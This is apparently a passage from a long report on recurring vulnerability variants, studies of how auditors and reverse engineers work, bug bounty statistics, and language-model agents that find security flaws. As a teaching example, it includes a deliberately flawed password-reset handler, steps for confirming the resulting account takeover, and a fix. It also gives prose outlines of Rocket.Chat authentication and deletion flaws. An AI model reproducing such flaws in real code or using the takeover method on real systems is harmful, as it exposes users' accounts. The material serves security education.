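Eight of the 17 variants in 2022 were close relatives of zero-days that attackers had already used in 2020 or 2021. (Google calls this more than 20% of the year's total, but 8 out of 41 is slightly less.)

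Some of these attacks took very little new work. Over two years, one group exploited four memory errors in JScript, an old component of Internet Explorer. In each case, JScript failed to track a value that was still in use. Microsoft's patch for the second error didn't stop the attack that had prompted it. In a Windows printing component, the old and new vulnerabilities differed mainly in the number identifying the type of message an attacker sent.

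Stone calls a patch "correct" if it fully prevents exploitation of the vulnerability, and "comprehensive" if it does so everywhere the same problem occurs. A patch for iPhones did not meet this standard because it set a maximum for a size but no minimum, the same omission as in wolfSSL's check of digest lengths. The first Log4j fix and the ruby-saml patch that kept both parsers were also incomplete by this standard.

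Later code changes can undo a complete patch. Stone describes a vulnerability in WebKit, the software behind Apple's Safari browser, that developers fully fixed in 2013. They reintroduced it three years later while reorganising the code, and fixed it again as a zero-day in January 2022. A test that repeated the original attack after every change would probably have caught the mistake.

The rise from 25% to 41% is weak evidence that patches got worse. Google suggests several other explanations, including that defenders had become better at recognising variants. The samples are also small, and the classification is partly a matter of judgement. Stone doubts that anyone exploited one of the six cases from 2020, a Firefox vulnerability, because nobody had found a way to trigger it without shutting down the affected process. All the figures leave out undetected attacks.

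*Look What You Made Us Patch* (Charrier, Sadowski and colleagues, 2026) gives more recent totals of 100 exploited zero-days for 2023, 78 for 2024 and 90 for 2025. These counts include all exploited zero-days, so they don't show whether the share of variants has changed. According to Zorz, the CISA review of August 2026 found that 41.5% of the entries in the agency's catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities belong to weakness types that have been common nearly every year since 2019. Unlike Google's figure, this doesn't measure variants, because two vulnerabilities of the same type can be unrelated.

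At least five of the six variants from 2020 were memory errors. The 2022 list is more mixed and includes a flaw in Microsoft's Exchange mail server that let attackers make the server send requests on their behalf. Netlas' *When Patches Fail* (2025) reports that Microsoft patched two vulnerabilities in SharePoint, its document-sharing system, on 8 July 2025, and that ten days later attackers were using variants that bypassed both patches. One of the patches was meant to fix authentication, so this pair included a logic flaw. According to CyberScoop, the security company VulnCheck ranked both variants among the ten most frequently targeted vulnerabilities of 2025.

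### Language models as variant hunters

Big Sleep, an AI agent that Google's Project Zero and DeepMind developed to find vulnerabilities, had its first public success in October 2024, in a variant analysis experiment. Google Project Zero (2024) explains that a known bug gives a language model a much more definite starting point than an open-ended request to find bugs.

The team collected recent changes to SQLite, a widely used database program, and removed the trivial ones. It gave the agent the description and text of a change and asked it to look for related problems that might remain in the current code. The agent, which used Google's Gemini 1.5 Pro model, could read the code and run test queries in a debugger.

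It found a memory error in a SQLite function. SQLite normally numbers the columns of a table from 0, but uses −1 for a row's built-in identifier. The function didn't allow for this value. It subtracted 1 and used the result, −2, as a position in an array, so it wrote to memory before the start of the array. A one-line query that looked up a row by its identifier could trigger the error. SQLite's developers fixed it the day they received the report, before the code had appeared in an official release.

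The agent could easily tell when it had triggered the bug. SQLite's developers had written an assertion, a line that stops the program if a condition is false, requiring this position to be between 0 and 2. The test version had assertions switched on, so the faulty query caused an immediate crash. Before the crash, the agent had suggested only vaguely that the problem might be "incorrect constraint handling", but afterwards it explained the cause accurately.

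This may not really have been a variant, since the team describes the bug as only loosely related to the change that the agent started from. It adds that studying one bug often leads human researchers to a different one too. A general-purpose fuzzer failed to find the bug in 150 hours of processor time, but it wasn't well suited to database queries, and the team thought a fuzzer built for SQLite would probably do at least as well as the agent.

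In July 2025 Google announced that Big Sleep had found another SQLite vulnerability, CVE-2025-6965. The Hacker News' *Google AI "Big Sleep" Stops Exploitation of Critical SQLite Vulnerability* (2025) describes it as memory corruption too, so neither discovery shows how well the agent can find logic flaws.

Snyk's May 2026 test on login software comes closer to addressing that question. Its most specific prompt in effect described a generalised root cause, and with it the model found a logic flaw that it had missed with broader prompts.

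Models don't reliably search for variants of their own findings, though. In Semgrep's tests on its most difficult codebase, the models found one missing ownership check but not the same omission elsewhere in the application, where an auditor would normally have looked next.

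## How expert auditors work

Researchers interview auditors or watch them work to learn how they decide where to look. Most of these studies describe a few people in detail, so they can show what some experts do but not how common those habits are.

In 2018 Daniel Votipka and colleagues at the University of Maryland reported interviews with 25 testers and hackers. The testers check software before its release, and the hackers look for vulnerabilities afterwards, often for a bug bounty. The researchers derived a process for finding vulnerabilities that was common to both groups. *The Industrial Age of Hacking* proposes adding a step in which people deliberately choose which software to examine. *Understanding Hackers’ Work* (2023), a similar study of twelve security professionals, argues that people who build automated tools first need to know how hackers think.

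### Watching 16 reverse engineers

Reverse engineers work out what a program does, usually without its source code or documentation. For *An Observational Investigation of Reverse Engineers' Processes* (2019), Votipka, Rabin and colleagues observed 16 of them, all with at least three years' experience. Eleven mainly looked for vulnerabilities, four analysed malware, and one did both. Each participant chose an interesting program they had recently analysed and repeated the analysis on a shared screen, while an interviewer with six years of reverse engineering experience asked about each decision. The sessions lasted 70 minutes on average.

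The participants' work fell into three phases:

- **Overview:** They first looked for the parts of the program that deserved attention. Fifteen listed the text it contained and the system functions it called, and seven ran it to see what it did. One saw a pop-up about the limits of the free version, then searched the code for those words, expecting to find the licence check nearby.
- **Sub-component scanning:** They skimmed the promising parts for familiar patterns and formed hypotheses about what the code did.
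- **Focused experimentation:** They tested particular hypotheses, and 13 did so by running the program under chosen conditions. The results usually raised new questions, which sent them back to scanning.

Many hypotheses turn out to be wrong. One participant suspected that a program could read memory before anything had been written to it. He traced the four paths through the function that was supposed to fill the memory. Two wrote a value, and the other two returned −1, which made the program exit before it reached the read, so there was no vulnerability.

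Votipka and colleagues never saw a participant go through more than 50 lines of code one by one. Six participants varied the program's inputs by hand, but only one used an automated fuzzer, and he waited until he understood the inputs and knew which part of the program to target.

*RE-mind* (2022) covers a larger group, 39 novices and 33 experts, who spent an average of nearly four hours each on two unfamiliar programs. It hypothesized that experts waste less time than novices on code that doesn't matter, not that they read faster. The earlier observations fit this hypothesis. For example, one of the 16 participants skipped any function that the program called from a hundred places, because it was probably routine error handling.

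The observations don't show which habits work best, since nobody compared the participants' success. People who are asked for an interesting example may also choose a job that went well.

### A procedure for finding logic flaws

The three phases can be turned into a procedure for auditing an application:

1. Learn what the system is for.
2. List who is trusted with what.
3. Find where the code assumes something.
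4. Try to violate each assumption.
5. Confirm the effect.

The second step isn't among the phases that Votipka and colleagues observed, but an auditor needs it to recognise a logic flaw.

Suppose an auditor is reviewing a payroll site that many companies use. From its owner, she learns that employees may read their own payslips and that payroll managers may also see their colleagues' payslips and change the bank accounts that wages go to. Anyone who has forgotten a password must prove that they control the email address on file. The code for this is:

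```python
@app.post('/forgot')
def forgot():
    user = User.find(email=request.form['email'])
    if user:
        token = new_random_token()
        ResetToken.save(token, user.id, expires=in_one_hour())
        send_link(user.email, token)
    return 'If you have an account, we have emailed you a link.'

@app.post('/reset')
def reset():
    record = ResetToken.find(request.form['token'])
    if record is None or record.expired():
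        return error(400)
    user = User.find(email=request.form['email'])
    user.set_password(request.form['new_password'])
    record.delete()
    return 'Your password has been changed.'
```

The emailed link opens a form that asks for a new password. The form also contains the token and the account's email address in hidden fields, which the browser sends back with the password.

The auditor goes through the code and writes down what has to be true for it to be safe:

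| Assumption | How she tries to violate it | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Nobody can guess a token | Read the function that generates tokens | Holds: each token contains 128 random bits |
| The link goes only to the address on file | Request a link and add a second address | Holds: the code takes the address from the user's record |
| A link works once, for an hour | Use a link twice, then try an old one | Holds |
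| A token changes the password only of the account it was issued for | Use one account's token with another account's address | Fails |
| A reset shuts out an intruder | Stay logged in on a second browser during a reset | The second browser stays logged in |
| Whoever receives mail at an address owns the account | Ask what companies do with the addresses of people who leave | Depends on the company |

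The fourth assumption fails because `reset` checks that the token is valid but then uses the email address from the form instead of the account number stored with the token. Several of the SAML products similarly verified one part of a document but used another.

To confirm it, the auditor uses two test accounts, much as one would for an insecure direct object reference:

1. She requests a link for Ben and opens it from Ben's inbox.
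2. She enters a new password, changes the hidden address to Alice's, and submits the form.
3. The site replies that the password has changed. This message doesn't prove much, so she logs in as Alice with the new password, and it works.
4. She repeats the request with an invented token, and the site refuses it.

The last step shows that the token check runs, so the flaw is that any valid token works for any account. An attacker would need only their own account and the victim's email address. An ordinary employee could take over a payroll manager's account and redirect everyone's wages. Replacing the second lookup in `reset` with `User.get(record.user_id)` fixes the flaw, so that changing the hidden address has no effect.

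The last two assumptions in the table are harder to settle. It may not matter that other browsers stay logged in after a reset if the owner intends resets only for people who have forgotten their passwords, but if customers also reset their passwords when they suspect a break-in, the intruder keeps his access. A company might also give a departed employee's email address to a new employee with the same name, who could then reset the old password and read the former employee's payslips. The auditor would be unlikely to think of this without knowing how companies manage email addresses.

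### What auditors remember

In the study of reverse engineers, 14 of the 16 used past experience to decide where to look. One had a list of iPhone system functions that programmers often misuse, and checked those first. Another noticed a function named `httpd_ipc_init` in a router's software. He knew that "IPC" usually stands for communication between processes, and that any process that could send messages to the web server might be able to attack it.

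When participants in the study by Votipka and colleagues didn't recognise anything, they used cruder methods, such as starting with the largest function. Votipka and colleagues relate this reliance on recognition to a theory that Klein and others developed from studies of firefighters and military officers. In that theory, experts recognise parts of a situation from earlier cases and quickly judge what to do, without comparing many options.

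Remembering past vulnerabilities helps auditors partly because developers tend to misunderstand the same things. The best evidence comes from a contest called Build It, Break It, Fix It, in which teams wrote programs to a common specification and then attacked one another's. Votipka, Fulton and colleagues (2020), in *Understanding security mistakes developers make*, spent about six months examining 94 of these programs. The tasks were to build a tamper-proof log, a link between a bank and its cash machines, and a database with access rules. Teams had just under two weeks to write their programs, and scored points for speed and features as well as security.

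The researchers counted 182 vulnerabilities, including some they found themselves, and classified them by cause:

| Cause | Number | Example |
|---|---|---|
| The team didn't attempt a necessary protection | 72 (40%) | 16 of the 52 log programs had no means of detecting tampering |
| The team misunderstood a protection | 71 (39%) | One program protected each log entry separately, so an attacker could still delete entries or change their order |
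| The team made a slip | 39 (21%) | One program checked whether it had seen a message's nonce before, but never recorded any nonces, so it accepted repeated messages |

Vulnerabilities of the first two kinds appeared in 78% of the programs, and slips appeared in 21%. An auditor could therefore find many vulnerabilities by checking for commonly misunderstood requirements. For example, if a program encrypts its messages, the auditor should ask whether an attacker could alter or repeat them, because encryption alone may not prevent either.

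The proportions depend on the task. Slips caused only 1 of the 53 vulnerabilities in the log programs but 22 of the 65 in the databases, the most complicated task. Commercial software is much larger than any of these programs, so slips may well be more common there. The researchers inferred the causes from the code. They presumed a team that left out a protection didn't know it was necessary, but some teams may have run out of time.

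Training didn't prevent these errors. *Build It, Break It, Fix It Contests* (2020) reports that many competitors had just finished a 24-week series of security courses. The lectures covered every protection that the tasks required, yet 55% of the teams from the courses left out at least one of the less obvious ones. Years of programming experience made no measurable difference either. Votipka and colleagues suggest that years may be the wrong measure of experience. In the 2018 interviews, the hackers' experience differed from the testers' mainly in the variety of vulnerabilities each group had found, read about or heard described.

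### What reviewers miss

The contest also gives some indication of how well people find each kind of error. On average, 27 teams per competition could read their rivals' source code. They exploited 38 of the 39 slips, but only 71% of the vulnerabilities caused by misunderstandings. One common misunderstanding was using a fixed value where the program needed an unpredictable one, and rivals exploited only 12 of those 26 cases.

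Teams may have noticed some of the other vulnerabilities but found them hard to exploit, and they scored only if they submitted a working attack. One log program had no protection against tampering, which is easy to see in the code. But it stored its entries in a structured format before encrypting them, and no team managed the attack, which required altering the encrypted text without breaking that format.

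Votipka and colleagues also cite a 2013 experiment in which researchers hired 30 developers to manually review the code of a small web application. It had seven known vulnerabilities of three types: SQL injection, cross-site request forgery, and cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's text runs as code in another user's browser. No reviewer found all seven, and the more experienced reviewers weren't necessarily more accurate. Reviewers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, so some may have done better simply by reporting more.

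These were web developers rather than specialist auditors, and all three types are well-known patterns, so the result is better evidence about ordinary code review than about experts looking for logic flaws. But even specialists miss a lot, as the smart-contract audit contests showed.

Reviewers can also miss types of vulnerabilities they know about, as Alberto Bacchelli of the University of Zurich says in PortSwigger's *The road to DevSecOps isn’t always the smoothest*, based on his group's earlier studies. In an online experiment, 146 participants, most of them software developers, reviewed code for a faulty check on user input. They did much better when the code made a possible attack easy to see. Warning them that the code contained a vulnerability also helped, though many still couldn't find it. This is a good reason to write down assumptions, because each one gives the reviewer something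 specific to check.

Adding reviewers helps less than one might expect. If each reviewer has probability *p* of finding a vulnerability, and they work independently, the chance that at least one of *n* reviewers finds it is

1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ.

If each reviewer independently has a 50% chance of finding any given vulnerability, three reviewers would find 87.5% of them on average. But suppose each reviewer has a 90% chance of finding the easy half and a 10% chance of finding the hard half. One reviewer still finds 50% on average, but three find only 63.5%, because they find 99.9% of the easy ones and 27.1% of the hard ones. A reviewer with different experience, who finds some of the hard ones easy, would be more useful than another with the same background.

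### Using tools and language models

The reverse engineers Votipka studied preferred tools that linked each result to a specific line of code. Fourteen of the 16 had to copy information by hand between the tool they used to read a program and the one they used to run it. In the contest study, Votipka and colleagues judged that the static analysers and fuzzers available in 2020 could have found some of the vulnerabilities, such as memory errors and missing error checks, but wouldn't have applied to most of them.

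Language models now do some of the code reading. In 2026, security engineers at Okta, which provides login services, ran two models on millions of lines of the company's own code, as Guillardoy and Nickels describe in *Hunting Vulnerabilities Using Frontier Models*. Okta had early access to both models, Mythos Preview and a cybersecurity version of OpenAI's GPT-5.5.

The engineers divided the search into steps, each in a separate session, and passed on only selected files so that too much information wouldn't lead the models to make worse decisions. Okta built four such sequences, which tended to find different kinds of vulnerability but produced many duplicates. It recorded every session, so an engineer who saw something interesting could reopen the search at that step and send the model in another direction.

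Some of the searches ran unsupervised. In others, an engineer who knew the code directed the model to a risky area, such as a complicated login process, or gave it hints about past vulnerabilities. Guillardoy and Nickels say the guided searches gave better results. Engineers often followed up a model's false report, supplied missing context, and found a real vulnerability nearby. So the engineers used the models for much of the scanning, but still chose many of the hypotheses and decided which results to believe.

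The account is informative about working methods but weak evidence that guidance helps. It doesn't include how many vulnerabilities were found, the false positive rate, or a controlled comparison of guided and unguided searches. The engineers were also working on their own company's software, which an outside auditor wouldn't know as well.

The models regularly rated their findings as more serious than they were. For example, a model might treat code as directly reachable from the internet when Okta had configured it differently. People checked the results and did all the triage by hand for any finding that might need a CVE entry. Okta's product security engineers spent many weeks triaging, reproducing and reporting the vulnerabilities.

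## What bug bounty data show and what they leave out

Most studies of auditors follow a few dozen people, whereas bug bounty platforms record tens of thousands of vulnerabilities a year. The platforms often present these records as evidence that finding access-control and logic flaws requires a person. The records show what outside researchers report and what companies will pay for. But they omit vulnerabilities that a company's own tools caught first, and the published totals rarely show how a researcher found a vulnerability.

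### How a report becomes a statistic

Suppose Alice discovers that she can read other customers' invoices on a shop's website, and reports this to the shop's bug bounty. YesWeHack's *The Trends, Insights and Strategic Shifts Shaping Offensive Security* (2026), the annual report of a European bug bounty platform, describes six steps of triage. The platform's analysts:

1. complete and standardise the details of her report;
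2. check that it follows the programme's rules, for example that the website is in scope and that this kind of vulnerability qualifies;
3. compare it with earlier reports, in case it's a duplicate;
4. reproduce the attack;
5. rate its severity;
6. advise the shop on the repair and the reward.

The shop then decides whether to accept the report and what to pay. It can also influence the severity rating, because the analysts defer to a customer who knows more about the system than they do. Of the reports YesWeHack counted in 2025, 12% were critical, 31% high, 49% medium and 8% low.

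Many submissions don't get through these steps. Wordfence (2026), which runs a bounty for add-ons to the WordPress website software, received 897 submissions in January 2026. It found 396 out of scope, rejected 277 and set aside 72 as duplicates, which left 152 (17%). On Standoff Bug Bounty, a Russian platform, 2,909 of the 7,870 reports submitted in 2025 (37%) were unique and accepted for payment, according to CNews' *Итоги года на Standoff Bug Bounty* (2026).

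Discarding duplicate reports loses some information about how hard flaws were to find. If five researchers report the same missing check, it was probably easy to find, but a tally of valid reports counts it once, just as it counts a flaw that a single expert found after a month's work.

### HackerOne's figures by class

HackerOne's *Hacker-Powered Security Report* (2025) covers July 2024 to June 2025, when the platform recorded about 84,900 valid reports and paid researchers $81 million. The table shows nine of the thirteen vulnerability classes in HackerOne's report. The last column gives the average reward per valid report in each class, counting any reports that earned nothing.

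| Class | Valid reports | Change in a year | Reward per valid report |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cross-site scripting (XSS) | 13,197 | −14% | $635 |
| Improper access control | 8,787 | +18% | $1,001 |
| IDOR | 6,016 | +29% | $1,265 |
| Business logic errors | 2,001 | +19% | $1,131 |
| Improper authentication | 1,737 | −9% | $1,355 |
| SQL injection | 1,213 | −23% | $1,074 |
| Improper authorization | 1,168 | −9% | $823 |
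| Code injection | 1,043 | −1% | $1,645 |
| Server-side request forgery (making a server send requests for the attacker) | 822 | About 0% | $1,851 |

Over five years, IDOR reports rose by 116% and improper access control by 66%, compared with 10% for XSS. Valid reports of all kinds grew by only 20% from 2021, so the platform's growth doesn't explain the rise in access-control reports.

Changes in labelling explain little of the rise in IDOR and improper access control reports. HackerOne says that researchers and analysts now classify authorization flaws more precisely, which moved some from "improper authorization" to those two labels. But going by the percentages, improper authorization reports fell by only about 115 in a year, while reports under the other two labels rose by about 2,700 combined.

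The ranking of classes is less informative because it depends on how finely one divides them. XSS is the largest single class, but IDOR and improper access control together are larger. An older ranking by HackerOne split XSS into subtypes, which put improper access control first with 13% of valid reports. The thirteen classes in the 2025 edition also cover only about 62% of that year's valid reports.

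HackerOne (2026) counted 92,194 valid reports and $89.1 million in payouts from July 2025 to June 2026, both about 10% more than the year before. The company's public summary doesn't break these totals down by vulnerability class. The best-known finding about logic flaws comes from the accompanying survey of 408 researchers, 72% of whom called business logic their fastest-growing category.

Business logic errors grew quickly, though more slowly than IDOR, and still made up only 2.4% of valid reports in the 2025 edition. In Help Net Security's *What human hackers still do better than AI, according to HackerOne’s CEO*, Kara Sprague calls the survey result "suggestive rather than conclusive" evidence of what is hard to automate.

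### Other platforms and other prices

Synack (2026), which sells security testing by vetted researchers and an AI agent, classified more than 11,000 vulnerabilities it found for customers in 2025. Injection accounted for 40.6% and broken access control for 32.8%. Help Net Security's *AI shrinks vulnerability exploitation window to hours* (2026) adds that XSS was the most common specific type in Synack's data, followed by authorization and permission problems. Synack presumably counts XSS as a form of injection, as OWASP does.

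On HackerOne, a similar grouping gives the opposite order. XSS, SQL injection and code injection make up about 18% of valid reports in the 2025 edition, while improper access control, IDOR, improper authorization and privilege escalation make up about 21%. On Standoff, access control flaws made up 58% of vulnerabilities of high or critical severity in 2025, according to CNews. These percentages show that access control flaws are common, but they don't support a more precise comparison because the customers, categories and totals all differ.

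HackerOne's figures also suggest that access-control flaws pay well, since an IDOR report earned about twice as much as an XSS report. Wordfence paid less for them in January 2026:

| Class | Findings | Average reward |
|---|---|---|
| Upload of a dangerous file | 4 | $1,314.75 |
| Improper privilege management | 4 | $707.50 |
| SQL injection | 5 | $166.00 |
| XSS | 43 | $91.40 |
| Missing authorization | 18 | $68.89 |
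| Authorization bypass by changing an identifier (IDOR) | 7 | $32.29 |

One reason may be that an attacker often needs an account to exploit an authorization flaw. Wordfence paid an average of $388.60 for vulnerabilities that anyone could exploit and $128.81 for those that required a subscriber's account. For example, a researcher received $195 for reporting a missing check in the Demo Importer Plus plugin that let any subscriber wipe a website and become its administrator.

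These are small numbers from a single month. It is also reasonable to count improper privilege management as an authorization flaw, and doing so changes the result. The three classes together then average $148, more than XSS and close to the programme's overall average of $142.

Rewards also depend on the company's industry. In HackerOne's 2025 figures, the median reward for a critical vulnerability was $60,000 at cryptocurrency and blockchain companies but $3,000 at telecommunications companies. A high average reward for a class of vulnerabilities is therefore poor evidence that they are hard to find. Server-side request forgery and code injection both earned more per report on HackerOne than IDOR or business logic vulnerabilities, although code injection is a common target for automated tools.

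### Why frequent reports don't show that tools failed

It's tempting to conclude that if researchers often report a kind of vulnerability, tools must be unable to find it. Suppose a group of websites contains *n* vulnerabilities of some class. The owners' tools remove a fraction *t* of them before researchers start looking, and the researchers report a fraction *r* of the rest. The number of reports is

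*n* × (1 − *t*) × *r*.

Bounty data show how many vulnerabilities researchers reported, but not how many tools had already found. If there are 200 vulnerabilities, the tools find none, and researchers report half, there will be 100 reports. There will also be 100 reports if there are 1,000 vulnerabilities, the tools remove 800, and researchers report half of the rest, even though the tools then found eight times as many as the researchers did.

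A class's share of reports is harder still to interpret, because it also depends on every other class. Suppose the websites contain only access-control flaws and XSS, and that between one year and the next the owners buy a better XSS scanner:

| | First year | Second year |
|---|---|---|
| Access-control flaws present | 200 | 200 |
| Removed by the scanner | 0 | 0 |
| Reported by researchers (half the rest) | 100 | 100 |
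| XSS flaws present | 1,000 | 1,000 |
| Removed by the scanner | 600 | 900 |
| Reported by researchers (half the rest) | 200 | 50 |
| Access control's share of reports | 33% | 67% |

The share doubles even though researchers report the same number of access-control flaws. This effect can't fully explain HackerOne's figures, because the number of IDOR reports rose too. But Synack's 32.8% and Standoff's 58% are shares, and they could be high partly because other vulnerabilities were easier to remove beforehand.

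Real programmes filter out easy vulnerabilities. YesWeHack says that companies often have professionals test a system heavily before opening it to bounty hunters. Sprague says in the Help Net Security interview that programmes now pay less, or nothing, for findings that can be automated. The same filtering affected the smart-contract audit contests.

Pay also influences what researchers look for. In a survey by Bugcrowd (2026), another bounty platform, 75% said hacking was becoming more about money than curiosity, though 85% considered reporting a critical vulnerability more important than making money. Of the 245 hunters surveyed by YesWeHack, 51% considered high rewards important when choosing a programme, and only 4% looked for long-established targets with many previous reports. Sprague says 68% of HackerOne's respondents had moved towards more complex, better-paid bugs because of AI.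 If so, *r* has risen for logic flaws and perhaps fallen for XSS, even if neither has become easier or harder for a tool to find.

HackerOne tried to measure the effect of rewards by examining 68 cases in which a programme cut them by at least 20%. Valid reports fell by an average of 22% between the 12 weeks before the cut and the 12 weeks after. The result for critical vulnerabilities is unclear. HackerOne says in one place that reports of them fell by half, and in another that half of the programmes saw a fall, which could easily happen by chance. It also doesn't compare these programmes with others that kept their rewards the same, so reports might have declined anyway as the programmes got older.

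Bounty data also mostly concern websites. Among YesWeHack's hunters, 98% were comfortable testing web applications, but only 20% were comfortable with open-source software or reviewing source code, and 6% with cryptography. HackerOne says its blockchain data underrepresent smart contracts. The figures are therefore relevant to access checks and single sign-on, but of little use for learning who finds faults like those in wolfSSL or Balancer.

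### Wrong labels and unpublished reports

Labels can also be wrong. Kaur confirmed only 84 of the 200 reports with access-control labels as broken object-level authorization. A first screening excluded 78. Of the 107 reports Kaur classified in full, 23 (21.5%) were also outside the study's definition.

That doesn't mean that 116 of the 200 labels were wrong, because Kaur was looking for access to a specific object belonging to someone else, and "improper access control" is a broader term. About 15 of the reports excluded at the start, for example, described ways around a login, which a researcher could reasonably have given that label. About 35 clearly described something different, such as XSS. If this sample is typical, at least one label in six is wrong. Errors like these inflate the number of access-control reports in any one year, but they wouldn't produce a rising trend unless people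 had become more careless about labeling.

People outside the platforms can check only the reports that companies choose to publish. Only one of the 84 reports Kaur studied came from financial services, although that sector's programmes paid researchers about $4 million, according to the 2025 edition of HackerOne's report. On YesWeHack, only 9% of programmes are open to everyone, and these supply 35% of the reports.

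### What the platforms sell

The companies that publish these figures have an interest in how people interpret them. HackerOne's subscription includes access to a community of researchers, according to AWS, which resells it. When HackerOne (2024) announced an earlier edition of its report, it claimed the report proved "how essential human expertise is". Synack ends the announcement of its figures by advertising an AI testing service backed by human researchers, whose judgement it says automation can't replicate.

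HackerOne is investing in testing by AI agents, as Sprague explains in McKinsey's *HackerOne CEO Kara Sprague on how AI is reshaping cybersecurity*, so it would also benefit if machines did more of the work. There's no particular reason to distrust the raw counts, but the commentary deserves more caution. For example, the 2025 edition calls business logic flaws "the premium battleground", but its table implies that the average reward for one fell by about 20% in a year.

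### AI-assisted reports

Until recently, one could fairly safely assume that a person, perhaps helped by tools, had found most of the vulnerabilities in these databases. HackerOne's 2025 data included a small exception, "hackbots", agents that look for vulnerabilities and submit reports themselves. Williams says in *How AI Security Is Transforming Offensive Security* that they submitted more than 1,100 reports, nearly half of them valid. XSS made up 78% of the valid hackbot reports, compared with about 16% of all valid reports on the platform.

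This is better evidence about automation than the overall counts, because we know a machine did the searching. It suggests that the agents of 2025 mostly found familiar types of bug, though their developers may have aimed them at XSS because it's easy to confirm.

The volume of reports then rose sharply. In *Navigating the AI Wave*, Lee (2026), HackerOne's head of operations, writes that AI-driven submissions began in February 2026, after a "human-only" period that lasted until January. The change was less abrupt than that, since 67% of researchers in HackerOne's 2025 survey already used AI or automation tools. *New HackerOne Signal Requirement for Vulnerability Reports* (2026) reports that the security team of Node.js, a widely used system for running JavaScript, received more low-quality reports over the December holidays than it could handle. Node.js responded by accepting reports only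 from researchers with a sufficient score for their past submissions.

By the third quarter of 2026, HackerOne was receiving 130% more submissions than a year earlier, according to Lee. Sprague told Help Net Security that submissions to bug bounty platforms had grown to 2.8 times their January 2025 level, and valid reports to 1.9 times. Suppose a programme received 100 submissions a month in January 2025, 25 of them valid. If it followed this pattern, it would now receive 280, about 48 of them valid. It would fix nearly twice as many vulnerabilities, but the valid share would have fallen from 25% to 17%, and its staff would have to handle 232 reports that weren't valid, up from 75.

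HackerOne gives a different impression in a press release, reporting that submissions reached a record in March 2026, up 76% in a year, while the share confirmed as exploitable held steady at about 25%. The two accounts may cover different periods or define a valid report differently. Sprague also mentions that a growing share of reports are still waiting for a decision, which lowers the valid share for now. That backlog might help explain why HackerOne's annual total of valid reports rose by only about 9%.

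Sprague says she can't reliably estimate how much of the increase comes from AI, because it's hard to tell whether a person, a model or both produced a report. So after February 2026, the number of valid reports in a class is no longer good evidence that people found the vulnerabilities, even before allowing for the tools that companies run first.

AI has probably also changed what researchers examine. Reports of vulnerabilities in source code tripled in a year, according to HackerOne. Lee notes that programmes covering open-source software get more duplicate reports than others, partly because several researchers run AI scanners on the same code. Ten researchers using the same model may therefore find little more than one would.

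The platforms have responded by making it harder to submit a report. YesWeHack can ban researchers who send in AI-generated findings they haven't verified by hand, and HackerOne now requires proof of identity for paid programmes. HackerOne also uses AI agents for part of its triage, to close reports that are clearly spam, duplicates or not security problems. Lee says the agents process close to half of all submissions and are at least as accurate as human analysts on these simpler decisions. If a researcher comments on a report that an agent closed, a person reviews it.

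## Whether finding these vulnerabilities requires a human

People found most of the vulnerabilities in the six cases, but that doesn't mean only a person could have found them. The work may need human understanding, or people may have found most of them because nobody had built a suitable tool. The cases suggest five explanations, which lead to different expectations about language models.

### Five explanations

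One explanation is that logic flaws produce no automatic failure signal. All six cases fit this explanation, and Log4Shell comes closest to an experimental test of it. The Jazzer fuzzer quickly rediscovered the flaw once it had a detector for remote lookups, even though it still had no information about what logging is for. This suggests that it had mainly lacked a signal, although people chose that signal already knowing about the flaw.

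Another explanation is that nobody has written down the specification. For example, only Acme can say whether its ordinary members may read its invoices. This explanation doesn't fit certificate checks well, because public standards set the minimum digest length that wolfSSL failed to enforce.

The facts needed to find a vulnerability may also be spread across files or organisations. Langfuse's blank setting was dangerous only because of how NextAuth handled it, and the mix-up attack on OAuth involves a shop and two identity providers. By contrast, the "goto fail" bug was one line in one function.

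Some attacks consist of many steps, each valid on its own. The Balancer attack took more than 65 small swaps, whereas reading someone else's invoice usually takes one request.

Finally, companies may have had little incentive to build better tools. A checker for one company's payroll rules is useful only to that company, while a memory-error detector works on almost any C program. Extending Jazzer was cheap, so cost can't have been the main obstacle, but nobody seems to have commissioned the extension before Log4Shell became famous.

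| Explanation | Cases that support it | Case that fits badly | Prediction for language models |
|---|---|---|---|
| No failure signal | All six, especially Log4Shell | None | They can find flaws by reading code, but report many false ones unless they can test an attack |
| Unwritten specification | Access checks, smart contracts | Certificate checks | They do well when a program's purpose is obvious and badly when the rule is one company's own |
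| Scattered facts | Single sign-on, access checks | "Goto fail" | They do worse as the facts spread out, and can't use facts that are outside the code |
| Long sequences of valid steps | Smart contracts, cryptographic protocols | Access checks | They improve as they get better at planning and can try each step |
| Weak incentives | Log4Shell, access checks | Cryptographic protocols, which have had specialised verifiers for decades | A general-purpose model quickly finds many old flaws at low cost |

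Better models should gradually overcome most of these obstacles. The exceptions are unwritten rules and facts that aren't in the code, since no amount of skill at reading code will reveal them. A human expert who has only the code is in much the same position, so the advantage lies with whoever can ask the code's owner.

### Logic flaws found by Mythos Preview

Carlini and colleagues claimed in April 2026 that Mythos Preview reliably distinguishes what code is meant to do from what it does. Their example is a login function that is meant to admit only authorized users but contains a way for others to get in. They reported web application flaws that let a stranger become an administrator, log in without a password or two-factor code, or delete data remotely. They don't give a success rate, so it's hard to know what "reliably" means, especially since they can't check logic flaws as conclusively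 as memory errors.

Nobody had patched the web application flaws at the time, so Carlini and colleagues withheld the details. For some other findings, including flaws in cryptography libraries, they published a hash of each report. Anyone can check a released report against its hash. A match proves that Anthropic had the document in April, but not that the document was correct, and Carlini and colleagues point out that the document could even be empty.

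Anthropic has since published several findings that resemble those descriptions. CVE-2026-29198 is a complete authentication bypass in Rocket.Chat, a workplace messaging system. Anthropic's *ANT-2026-GEM3N3N3 · rocketchat/rocket.chat* (2026) explains that a server with OAuth login identified users by looking up their access tokens in a database, but didn't check that the token in a request was plain text. An attacker could instead send a search condition that matched any non-empty token. The database returned the first match, usually the administrator's token, so one request could give a stranger full control.

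This is weaker evidence about understanding intentions than it seems. The vulnerability comes from a form of injection, which Carlini and colleagues consider so similar to memory corruption that they don't discuss it at length. Anthropic also credits the discovery to Claude but doesn't say which model.

CVE-2026-48929, also in Rocket.Chat, is a better test. Anthropic's *ANT-2026-QXNF2N9K · rocketchat/rocket.chat* (2026) credits it to Mythos Preview. In outline, the code for deleting an attached file was:

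```js
if (msg && userId) {
    // stop unless this user may delete the message
}
FileUpload.deleteById(fileID)
```

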